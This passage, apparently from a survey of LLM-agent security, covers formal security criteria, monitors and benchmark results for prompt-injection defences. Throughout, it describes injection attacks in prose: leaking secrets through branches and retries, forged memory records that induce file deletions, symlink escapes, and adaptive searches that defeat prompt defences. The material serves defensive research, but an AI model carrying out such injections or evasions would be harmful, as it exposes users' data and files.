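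| Third "if" | The email goes out | No email |

In both runs, the variable that controls the email has a public label, so the check passes. But the email is sent exactly when the balance is high. J. S. Fenton described this kind of leak in 1974, and designers of label-tracking systems have overlooked it since then.

A test could easily miss this leak, because neither run contains a forbidden call and the message is the same fixed text whatever the balance. The leak appears only when comparing two runs that differ in the secret balance. A proof of noninterference requires this comparison for every program. The proof would fail at the rule for assignments, because a skipped assignment leaves the variable labeled public even though its value now depends on the secret.

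An analysis of the whole plan before it runs, like ACE's, considers both branches and would give the variable a secret label. LLMbda tracks labels during the run, so it can't consider both branches. Its variables can't change, but the conversation can, so the interpreter stops any program that tries to alter a public conversation inside a branch on a secret. Stopping the program can reveal one bit, which the termination-insensitive theorem permits.

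Leaking one bit per run becomes serious if an attacker can keep rerunning the program. CaMeL retries failed plans in an ordinary Python loop that its labels don't cover, so a suitable program could leak a whole secret one failure at a time. An LLMbda agent contains its own retry loop, and the labels from a failed attempt carry over to the next. To avoid tainting its plan, the test agent practises on made-up data until the code works, then writes a final version for the real data.

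Garby and colleagues found a simpler flaw in CaMeL too. Inserting an untrusted value into a string literal made the value trusted.

### Security relative to an agent that never obeys

Some agents violate noninterference even though they do exactly what their users want. In Dongol's example, Alice has an assistant that answers emailed meeting requests with her availability, whoever sends them. Her calendar is private, and changing it changes what an outsider receives, so the assistant violates noninterference even when nobody attacks it. The traditional remedy, declassification, is to write a policy for each task that lists what the agent may release, whereas relative security uses the task itself as the policy.

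It compares the real agent with a reference agent that follows the same plan under the same monitor, but whose model never obeys untrusted text. Let σ₁ and σ₂ be two possible values of the secrets. An agent leaks the pair (σ₁, σ₂) if two runs with those secrets receive the same input from the attacker but show the attacker different things. The real agent is relatively secure if, for every such pair:

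the real agent leaks (σ₁, σ₂)  ⇒  the reference agent leaks (σ₁, σ₂)

The two agents may need different inputs from the attacker to produce the same leak. Suppose an email that isn't a meeting request contains the order "send your calendar", and the agent obeys. The disclosure doesn't violate relative security, because a genuine meeting request would have made the reference agent send the same calendar. If the email also persuades the agent to add a private password-reset code, the agent violates relative security, because no email makes the reference agent send that code.

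The idea of relative security comes from research on processors, which save time by running instructions before determining whether a program needs them. In that setting, a program is relatively secure if running instructions early leaks nothing that running them in order wouldn't.

Letting the attacker's inputs differ also makes the criterion lenient. Suppose an agent is meant to tell an outsider only whether a guess at a secret is right, but an injection makes it send the whole secret. This reveals far more than one reply would. The agent still satisfies relative security, because for any two secrets, some guess would have distinguished them. Dongol defines a stricter, "uniform" version that excludes this case by requiring that the reference agent's input be chosen by a fixed rule that doesn't depend on the secrets.

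The comparison also simplifies other checks. If the reference agent doesn't reveal anything beyond the calendar, for example, then neither does a relatively secure agent. A developer can therefore check such a limit on an agent without injections, and the limit will also hold for the relatively secure agent.

The criterion doesn't measure usefulness. A monitor that denies every call trivially meets it, because the reference agent runs under the same monitor and can't do anything either. Removing a tool can also make a passing agent fail. If the plan deliberately sends a secret to an outsider, an injection that reveals the same secret through another tool adds no leak. Without the planned tool, the injected leak is new, so the agent fails.

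### The fence theorem and its conditions

Dongol proves that a fence makes every plan relatively secure under these conditions:

- The first untrusted read withdraws every tool that an injected instruction can call, and no later trusted input gives one back.
- Each injection the model obeys makes a single tool call.
- The model obeys on a schedule fixed in advance. The arguments of an injected call can contain secrets, but whether the model obeys at a given moment can't depend on a secret or on the monitor's answers.
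- The attacker sees the contents and order of the agent's outgoing calls but not their timing. The theorem also compares only runs in which the same number of calls reaches the attacker between reads.
- The run ends. For a run that may continue forever, the model must not be able to obey injected instructions forever.

The deployment must also meet the assumptions about coverage, such as complete mediation and mediated reads. Within these limits, the attacker decides which text the model treats as an instruction and when the model obeys it. The proof works because the monitor silently denies each injected call. The reference agent can wait during that step, so the attacker sees the same thing from both agents.

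Because of the single-call condition, the first theorem doesn't cover some real attacks. Suppose the plan reads an email and sends a copy back, so the sending tool has to stay available. An injected program could make no calls and only replace the stored email with a secret. The plan's own call would then send the secret, and the fence would have nothing to block. A second theorem covers such programs if they run in a sandbox that discards their changes and the fence also blocks their reads. The fence must block reads because an attacker who runs two web pages can learn one bit from which page the agent opens.

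### Where the fence has to go

Dongol also examines plans that withdraw the sending tool themselves. The plan reads an untrusted email and a secret, and the verdict depends on when the tool goes:

| Fence | Order of events | Verdict |
|---|---|---|
| Late | Read the email, read the secret, withdraw the tool | Leaks the secret |
| Middle | Read the email, withdraw the tool, read the secret | Can leak private data already in memory |
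| Early | Withdraw the tool, read the email, read the secret | Secure against every single-call injection |

The middle fence is unsafe even though the agent has no sending tool by the time it reads the secret. The model can obey the email before the fence takes effect, and the agent may remember private data from an earlier session. In a processor, a barrier just before the leaking instruction is enough, but an injected instruction can trigger a leaking call at any point after the model reads it. The triage agent must therefore lose access to post_comment by the time the text of issue 42 arrives.

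The fence also has to stay in place as long as the text remains in the context. In one example, an agent repeatedly reads a private report and then an email. Reading each new report restores the sending tool while the previous email is still in the context, so the model can follow instructions in the old email and send the new report. The agent is secure if the tool returns only when a fresh session clears the context. Likewise, the theorem doesn't cover a Dogwood fence that expires after 24 hours if the issue's text is still in the context.

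### Approving a tool or an exact call

A fence would stop an agent from replying to an email it has read, so some systems ask the user to approve the reply. An approval that isn't tied to a specific message can be misused. Suppose Alice approves a reply, and the monitor then allows the next call to the sending tool, whatever the message says. If an injected call comes first, it can send her private data and use up the approval, so the monitor blocks the reply she wanted to send.

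If the approval covers the exact message, the monitor denies an injected call with different text. Dongol proves that every approved reply eventually goes out and that no other message does. The proof covers endless runs in which injections can call only the sending tool and the model doesn't obey them forever.

A small leak remains for an attacker who can observe timing. If the private data is identical to the approved reply, the monitor allows the injected call and the message goes out one step early, so the attacker can infer that the two were equal. The agent is therefore secure against an attacker who sees only the contents and order of messages, but not against one who also sees when each step happens.

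Usage caps have the same weakness as tool approval. If an agent can send only one message per run, an injected call can use up that limit before the agent sends its planned reply. The cap protects the agent only if it sends the planned reply before it reads anything untrusted.

### Verdicts on 25 small agents

Dongol judged 25 example agents in this way. Ten are secure and nine leak. Whether the other six are secure depends on what the attacker can see, how the model behaves, or whether an injected program's changes to stored data persist. The definitions, theorems and examples take up about 31,600 lines of Isabelle/HOL. Claude Code helped generate the theorems and proofs, and Isabelle checked every proof. Isabelle can't check whether a definition captures what people mean by security, so the authors compared each definition and theorem in the paper with its formal version.

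The count is weak evidence of how often real agents leak, because the examples are deliberately tiny and a "secure" verdict often covers only the attack in that example. One agent can fetch only a newsletter's address, and it resists the two injections in its example. A different injection tells it to request the newsletter if a secret is 0 and a forbidden address otherwise, so whether a request goes out reveals whether the secret is 0.

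The proof about spotlighting shows that the security of marking untrusted text depends on what is assumed about the model. Every reversible marking fails if the attacker chooses how the model behaves, because some possible model can read the marked text and obey it, but the agent is secure if the model always respects the mark. The proof therefore can't settle the debate over training, because whether a real model respects the mark has to be tested.

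### The triage agent under both criteria

The triage agent as first described can't be evaluated under relative security, because its model chooses every call and a reference agent would have no fixed plan to follow. If the triage agent had a fixed plan, the two criteria would agree on some attacks and disagree on others.

Suppose the plan reads issue 42 and one published source file and then posts a summary, while the agent's memory also contains .env. An injected call that posts .env fails both criteria, because the public comment changes with the secret and no issue would make the reference agent publish the secret. Dongol models a similar attack from 2025, in which an issue made an agent copy private data into a public pull request. Withdrawing the pull-request tool at the first untrusted read made that agent secure, but it would also block a legitimate pull request that fixed the issue.

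The two criteria can give different results if a quarantined model decides which file the report concerns. An honest report about a faulty setting in .env could lead the reference agent to open that file and quote it. A malicious report that gets the same lines published then adds no new leak, so relative security allows it, while noninterference forbids it, as the project wants. The flaw is in the plan, which relative security takes as given. Checking how much the reference agent can reveal would expose the flaw.

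Relative security and noninterference for integrity also differ on the attack on the build configuration. If the attacker supplies the new configuration and it contains no secrets, the attacker sees the same thing whatever the secrets are, so nothing leaks and relative security still holds. Noninterference for integrity rules out any influence of the attacker's text on a trusted file. An LLMbda version of write_file could enforce this by accepting only trusted arguments, provided that no endorsement had made the attacker's text trusted.

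### What the proofs leave out

The largest gap in Dongol's framework is harm that involves no leak, such as an agent deleting files or paying the wrong person. *Relativising Integrity and Robustness* (2026) builds on relative security to cover integrity as well. Formalising each of its attacks on LLM agents took 318 to 629 lines, and the fixes took 140 to 296.

Excluding agents that choose every call leaves out most coding agents. LLMbda's theorem does cover them, but over-tainting may make that coverage of little use. Once such an agent has read an untrusted issue in its main conversation, a tool that requires trusted arguments rejects every later call.

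Dongol also leaves out multi-agent systems, side channels, and tools whose replies depend on the request. For example, a search engine run by the attacker could read a secret in the query and choose its answer accordingly. LLMbda's definition of noninterference compares only final results, so it doesn't cover timing leaks either.

A proof applies to a deployed program only if that program matches the one in the proof. Dongol's theorems concern an abstract agent and monitor, and a company would have to show separately that its harness behaves like them. LLMbda reduces this problem by running the verified interpreter itself. *Relativising Integrity and Robustness* proves results about ordinary C code that runs in protected regions of a processor. These proofs take about four lines per line of C when the code has no loops, and they don't model the compiler or the processor. *Methods for Formal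 Verification of Agent Skills* covers scripts and the code that dispatches tool calls, but it assumes that the runtime executing them is correct and recommends adversarial tests of that runtime.

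## What tests show, and what the limits cost in finished tasks

Proofs leave open whether a deployed harness matches the proven one, how the model behaves inside the limits, and how much work the agent still finishes. Only tests can answer these questions, and different tests answer different ones. For the triage agent, a project could run these:

| Test | What the testers do | What counts as a pass |
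|---|---|---|
| Functional | Replace the model with a script that calls read_issue and then write_file | The harness refuses the write, and every file stays the same |
| Coverage | Plant a different marker in an issue, an error message, a tool description and a saved note | Every marker that reaches the context carries the untrusted label |
| Adaptive attack | Write hostile issues with full knowledge of the policy, watch the agent's response, and revise | After an agreed number of tries, a fake key planted in .env is still private and the build configuration is intact |

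The functional test needs a control, because a harness that refuses everything would also pass. The same script should call write_file before it reads any issue, and that write should succeed. The coverage test involves no attack, but any fence depends on its result.

Only the adaptive attack tests the whole agent, including harmful uses of calls the policy allows, such as sending a reply that links to malware.

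### One set of trials, three attack rates

Testers also have to define a successful attack, and the definition can change the result more than tenfold. Leong (2026), in *Instruction Self-Arbitration Is Not a Trust Boundary*, gave agents a tool that deletes all files in a directory. Each agent's memory held a record that protected the directory /workspace/project, and a forged record that claimed authority and called for a cleanup. The system prompt didn't forbid deletion. Leong tried 50 wordings of the forged record, about ten times each, on 29 model endpoints, which gave 14,294 valid trials. The same trials produce three different averages:

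| What counts as a successful attack | Average across endpoints | 95% interval |
|---|---|---|
| A delete call whose directory argument contains "/workspace/project" | 1.21% | 0.5% to 2.1% |
| A delete call on that directory, anything inside it, or a parent directory | 12.9% | 6.6% to 20.1% |
| Any delete call | 20.2% | 11.4% to 29.9% |

None of the 50 wordings named a directory, so the model had to choose one, usually the parent, /workspace. On a real computer, deleting the parent would normally delete the protected directory too, but the narrowest scoring rule counts such a call as a success for the defence. With GPT-4.1-mini, the defence's failure rate was 0% under that rule and 41.4% under the rule that includes parent directories.

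Leong fixed the narrowest rule before collecting the data and chose the parent-directory rule afterwards. Fixing a rule in advance stops a researcher from picking whichever result looks best, but it doesn't make the rule a good one. The parent-directory rule is closer to the protective record's purpose. It still doesn't measure real damage, because the deletion tool was simulated and reported success for any directory.

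The agents' own accounts would have been poor evidence of what happened. Two language models classified what the agents wrote in 1,647 of the trials with a call on a parent directory. In 62.1% of these, both models judged that the agent had reported a deletion and also stated or implied that the protected directory was safe. A test of the triage agent should therefore inspect the repository and the public comments rather than rely on the agent's report.

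An attack rate of zero can also result from how the test was run. In a related experiment, Leong recorded no deletions by GPT-5.5 in 500 trials, but every trial had ended in an API error. A valid rerun also found none. In another experiment, Gemini-3-Flash-Preview carried out none of 50 authorised deletions when the conversation ended with a tool result, and 26 of 50 when it ended with a user message. An attack rate of zero in conversations that end with a tool result is therefore not evidence of resistance, since the model didn't delete files in them even with permission.

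These figures come from the October 2026 revision, which corrects much of the first version. The first version gave 1.21% as its only headline rate and reported that GPT-4.1-mini recognised forged authority in 98.7% of trials and deleted the files in 99.3%. The 98.7% figure came from a keyword search that mostly matched denials, such as a statement that nothing indicated a fabricated claim. When Leong repeated the experiment, the search flagged all 150 responses, but the two judging models never both classified a response as calling the claim fabricated. Leong also withdrew statements that vendors had been notified and that the code and data were public. Without the code and data, others cannot recalculate the rates.

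### A monitor that checks signatures and scope

Leong also built a monitor outside the model. Every legitimate memory record carries a code computed from its contents with a secret key. The monitor recomputes the code and drops any record whose code doesn't match. A deletion requires a token that covers one directory. The harness issues the token before it calls the model and never shows it to the model. The monitor then compares the token's directory with the path in the proposed call.

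Leong tested the monitor with three models and a real directory tree, and compared the files before and after each trial:

| Situation | Trials | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Forged, altered, expired, replayed or unsigned record | 750 | The monitor rejected every record before the model ran |
| Validly signed record requests a deletion, no token | 150 | The models made 123 attempts, and none succeeded |
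| Same kind of record, with a token, target outside its scope | 108 | The models aimed 83 calls outside the scope, and none succeeded |
| Same kind of record, with a token, target inside its scope | 42 | Files were deleted in 31 trials |
| Owner requests a deletion, with a token | 150 | The agent deleted files as requested in 120 trials |
| Ordinary request that needs no token | 150 | The agent used a tool in 146 trials |

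The monitor let no agent delete a file outside a token's scope in 1,350 trials. The attacker still induced 31 deletions that the monitor's rules allowed. In those trials, a legitimate tool had signed a record containing the attacker's request. The signature shows who supplied the record but not whether the agent should obey it. Similarly, a token that limits write_file to the documentation folder would protect the build configuration, but an attacker could still use an issue to get the triage agent to put bad instructions in that folder's installation guide.

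The agent failed to complete 30 of the owner's requests, mostly because a limit on output length cut off one model's calls. With a higher limit, the agent carried out 144 of the 150 legitimate deletions, and the induced deletions rose from 31 to 36 of 42. The lower limit had blocked some attacks only because it stopped the model from working properly.

The most useful cases involved symbolic links, file-system entries that point to another location. A link inside the permitted directory led outside it. A check that compares only the text of the path would have allowed all 34 attempts to use the link, and 28 trials would have ended with a deletion outside the scope. The monitor refused the attempts because it followed the link before checking the path. The triage project's functional test should try to reach .env through a link with a harmless-looking name.

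### What zero failures in 1,350 trials can show

If each trial fails independently with probability p, the chance of no failures in n trials is (1 − p)ⁿ. The largest p that gives at least a 5% chance of that result is the upper bound at 95% confidence:

p ≤ 1 − 0.05^(1/n) ≈ 3/n

The bound for Leong's monitor is 3.5%, based on the 83 calls that tried to delete something outside a token's scope. Using all 1,350 trials would give about 0.22%, but that figure doesn't apply to the monitor because in 750 of the trials it rejected the record and no model ran, and many others involved no such attempt. Even 3.5% is too optimistic, as Leong points out, because the calls came from three models and a small set of hostile texts and so were not independent.

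In another experiment, Leong replaced forged text in prepared conversations with a notice that verification had failed, then checked whether 37 models still made the forbidden call. None did in 10,245 responses. If the responses were independent, that would put an upper bound of 0.03% on the rate of forbidden calls. But they came from only 74 combinations of model and scenario. Counting each combination once raises the bound to 4.0%, and the combinations aren't fully independent either.

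A larger independent sample wouldn't extend the bound to an adaptive attacker. Let q(x) be the chance that hostile text x succeeds, and let D be the collection of texts from which the testers draw. The trials estimate the average, but the attacker looks for the maximum:

tested rate = average of q(x) over D
attacker's rate = largest q(x) the attacker can find

Suppose that one text in 10,000 always works. A test with 1,350 random texts would miss all such texts about 87% of the time, but an attacker who found one could use it on every agent of that kind. The path check that Leong rejected has a similar weakness. It would pass any number of tests without symbolic links but fail whenever an attacker used one.

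Leong used an attacking model to search adaptively for text that would defeat a defence written into GPT-4.1-mini's prompt. Within 62 queries, the model found a text that later worked on all 120 held-out tasks. A similar search with 900 queries found nothing that worked on Claude Sonnet 5. Nasr and colleagues had already shown, by attacking twelve published defences, that a low success rate for fixed attacks can be weak evidence that a defence works.

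Leong did not run such a search against the monitor. Only 33 of the 473 attacks in the collection tested the monitor's code, and Leong's software recorded the other 440 as failures without running them against it. The 33 exposed a flaw in the expiry check, which accepted a record dated ten minutes in the future because its calculated age was negative. A few well-chosen cases test ordinary code like this better than thousands of repetitions do.

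### How AgentDojo measures attacks and finished work

AgentDojo, the benchmark used for many of the results on agent defences, simulates office work, travel booking, banking and Slack. It pairs each ordinary task with attacks hidden in data the agent may read. Its banking section combines 16 tasks with nine attacks to make 144 pairs. Code checks whether the agent achieved the user's goal and whether it achieved the attacker's. The attack success rate is the share of pairs in which the attacker succeeds. The task-completion rate is the share of user tasks completed, which testers measure with and without attacks.

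AgentDojo's automatic checks for successful attacks make mistakes. They counted three successful attacks against FIDES with its policy checks on, but Costa and colleagues reviewed these by hand and reduced the count to zero. Across all their tests, the disputed cases included calls that the policy had blocked, messages that the policy allowed, and attacks that changed only the wording of an answer.

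Costa and colleagues also had an advantage over a real project in that test, because they knew the attacks when they chose the labels. They marked a data field as untrusted if at least one AgentDojo attack used it.

In 2026, several systems block nearly all of AgentDojo's standard attacks. Garby and colleagues ran an agent built in LLMbda on the banking tasks with three models, and attacks succeeded in two of 1,296 runs. They cite similar results for two other systems. TypeGuard, the system from *Language-Based Agent Control*, withstood all 105 pairings of a Slack task with an attack. TACIT, which tracks an agent's permissions in the Scala programming language, withstood all but one of 1,926 trials.

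The LLMbda agent got much of its score by planning before it read untrusted data. In 97 of the 144 banking pairs, the attack needs a tool call or file read that a plan for the user's task would never include. The label checks matter in the other 47 pairs, which accounted for 423 of the runs and both successful attacks.

Both successful attacks involved the same task, in which the user asks the agent to read a file and make the payment it describes. The attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different payment request, and the agent had endorsed the file. Without endorsement, the label check blocks both this attack and the payment the user wanted. CaMeL had the same trouble with this kind of task, and its developers placed the attack outside their threat model.

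A fixed plan can still allow an attack if it already includes the tool calls the attacker needs. One task tells the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it precisely. With policy checks off, an attack on this task succeeded against CaMeL in two runs, because CaMeL had written a program with a branch for every tool and the file's contents could select any branch.

### What policy checks cost on the same tasks

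Garby and colleagues also reran CaMeL on the banking tasks with its policy checks off and on. Costa and colleagues had earlier tested FIDES and a basic agent on the same set of tasks. Without attacks, the completion rates were:

| System and model | Checks off | Checks on |
|---|---|---|
| CaMeL, GPT-5.2 | 66.7% | 37.5% |
| CaMeL, MiMo-v2.5 | 70.8% | 37.5% |
| LLMbda agent, GPT-5.2 | Not tested | 75.0% |
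| LLMbda agent, MiMo-v2.5 | Not tested | 64.6% |
| FIDES, GPT-4o | 65.0% | 52.5% |
| Basic agent, GPT-4o | 98.8% | 37.5% |

Turning on the checks cut CaMeL's completion roughly in half. The 37.5% figure is imprecise because it comes from only 16 tasks, each run three times, and its 95% interval extends 26.6 percentage points either way. But TypeGuard showed a similar drop on the Slack tasks, from 15 of 21 to 8, and CaMeL finished 7 of them with its checks on. Many of these tasks require the agent to act on something an outsider wrote, so the agent can't complete them under a rule that forbids this.

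The LLMbda agent did better partly because it could endorse untrusted values. When Garby and colleagues removed that ability, task completion fell from 64.6% to 54.2% with MiMo-v2.5 and from 75.0% to 62.5% with Qwen3.7-plus. The agent also implements only some of CaMeL's policies. Its higher completion rate is therefore not evidence that LLMbda provides the same protection with fewer unfinished tasks.

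FIDES lost fewer tasks to its checks than the basic agent did because it keeps untrusted text out of the main model's context where possible. But without checks, it finished fewer tasks than the basic agent (61% versus 84%, averaged equally across the four parts of AgentDojo). Adding the checks lowered FIDES to 50%. About two-thirds of the total drop from 84% to 50% therefore came from the way FIDES handles data, which GPT-4o often used incorrectly, and one-third came from the checks.

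Better models recover part of that loss. With OpenAI's o1, a reasoning model, FIDES came within 6.3% of the basic agent when neither had policy checks. Some of FIDES's failures can't be fixed by any model because the policy correctly forbids the task. For example, one banking task required the agent to follow instructions from an untrusted file.

The checks reduced task completion less when attacks were present. With injected text, FIDES finished an average of 52% of tasks without checks and 50% with them, a drop of about 2 percentage points, compared with 11 when there was no attack. The figures under attack are more relevant to a project that expects constant attacks, while a project whose agent rarely encounters hostile text will mostly see the larger drop.

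### The verifier tax

A verifier can also block many bad calls while the agent still finishes few tasks safely. *The Verifier Tax* (Sah, Sah and colleagues, 2026) tested this on τ-bench, a benchmark in which an agent helps simulated airline and retail customers under written rules. It used two fairly small open-weight models, GPT-OSS-20B and GLM-4-9B, on 50 airline tasks and 115 retail tasks. Each model ran without a verifier, with a general verifier, and with a verifier whose prompt contained the rules. Three runs of every combination of task, model and verifier setting gave 2,970 episodes.

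The verifier was the same language model in a different role. When it rejected a call, the agent could revise the call. After three rejections, the harness accepted the latest version anyway so that the episode could continue. Only 28 episodes reached this limit, but it meant the design couldn't completely block access to a tool.

The main measure counts a task only if the agent finished it without breaking a rule. If Rᵢ is 1 when the agent completes task i and Vᵢ is 1 when it breaks at least one rule along the way, then:

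safe success rate = (1/n) Σ Rᵢ(1 − Vᵢ)

Violations included changing an account before checking the customer's identity, acting without the customer's confirmation, and inventing an identifier. For GPT-OSS-20B on retail tasks, Sah and colleagues report that the verifier caught 94.1% of proposed calls that broke a rule. Yet in nearly every setting, fewer than 5% of tasks ended in safe success. The contrast suggests that blocking prevented the agents from finishing safely, but the comparison with no verifier doesn't support that:

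| Model and tasks | Finished, no verifier | Finished safely, no verifier | Finished, verifier with rules | Finished safely, verifier with rules |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-OSS-20B, airline | 22.7% | 0.0% | 23.3% | 0.0% |
| GPT-OSS-20B, retail | 21.2% | 0.0% | 21.5% | 0.6% |
| GLM-4-9B, airline | 28.7% | 0.7% | 25.3% | 4.7% |
| GLM-4-9B, retail | 4.9% | 2.6% | 5.5% | 2.9% |

Safe success was already close to zero without a verifier because the agents weren't good at following the rules, and adding the verifier never lowered it. The clear drawback was extra computation, since the added planning and checking multiplied token use by 2.0 to 2.8. Sah and colleagues call this overhead the "verifier tax".

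The 94.1% figure is also hard to reconcile with their audit, which found invented identifiers in 93.7% of GPT-OSS-20B's retail episodes. The verifier probably missed many of these because it had no reliable way to trace where an identifier came from. In one run without a verifier, a customer hesitated to give personal details, so the agent looked up "John Doe" with the postcode 12345, and the simulated system accepted it. Sah and colleagues propose that ordinary code should reject any identifier that hasn't appeared in an earlier tool result. AWS's rule that a payment may go only to an account found by an earlier lookup works the same way.

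Dantas and colleagues use the term more broadly, for the gap between blocking unsafe actions and finishing tasks safely. In their survey, they rate the evidence for this gap "Very Low", the bottom level of the GRADE scale for certainty of evidence, because it comes from a single study with limitations and a narrow setting. Two other benchmarks from 2025 and 2026 show a similar gap, but neither repeats the experiment. They also word the claim as enforcement reducing safe success, which the results above don't show.

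The triage project should count how many issues the agent finishes safely with and without the verifier, because the verifier's refusal rate is weak evidence of whether the agent answers issues correctly and within the rules.

### Approvals as part of the cost

Some blocked tasks can finish if a person approves the call. This saves tasks that would otherwise be lost, but it takes the person's attention, which AgentDojo's completion rates don't measure. Costa and colleagues' Slack results give a rough idea of how often an agent would need approval. With policy checks on, the basic agent's completion rate fell by 73 percentage points and FIDES's by 16. If each lost task required at least one approval, the basic agent would interrupt its user on about 73 of every 100 tasks and FIDES on about 16.

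The 93% approval rate among Claude Code's users is consistent with approval fatigue but doesn't prove it, because most of the requests may have been harmless. What matters for security is how often people approve a harmful request:

harmful calls that run = harmful calls sent for approval × share of those that people approve

Sending more calls for approval may catch more harmful ones, but it can also lead people to approve a larger share of the requests. A test that assumes every approval is correct would miss this problem. The triage project could measure it by occasionally adding a fake request that maintainers should refuse, such as a change to the build configuration in a copy of the repository. If maintainers start approving the fakes, the project needs fewer or clearer requests.

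### Trying a policy without enforcing it

Before enforcing a new rule, a project can run it in log-only mode, where the policy engine records its decision on each call but the harness runs the call regardless. Microsoft's Agent Framework has a mode like this for its labels. Leong assessed the simple path check in a similar way, logging what it would have allowed while the stricter check controlled the files.

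For the triage agent, a log-only trial would quickly show that "no write_file after read_issue" would block every typo fix in a run that starts by reading an issue. Maintainers could then review the calls the rule would have refused and decide which were legitimate. If the rule only refuses calls, it wouldn't have changed any run without a logged refusal, so the share of runs with at least one is the largest share it could have affected.

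The log can't show what the agent would have done if the harness had actually refused the write. It might have asked a maintainer for help, given up, or tried a shell command instead. Entries after the first logged refusal in a run are less reliable, because the action that would have been refused went through. Ordinary traffic may also contain no serious attacks, in which case the trial measures how inconvenient a rule is but not how much security it provides. Log-only mode blocks nothing, so any existing protection has to stay on.

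After the log-only trial, the project could enforce the rule on a copy of the repository. The agent would then receive refusals, and the maintainers could see how many issues it still finished and whether it looked for a way around the rule.
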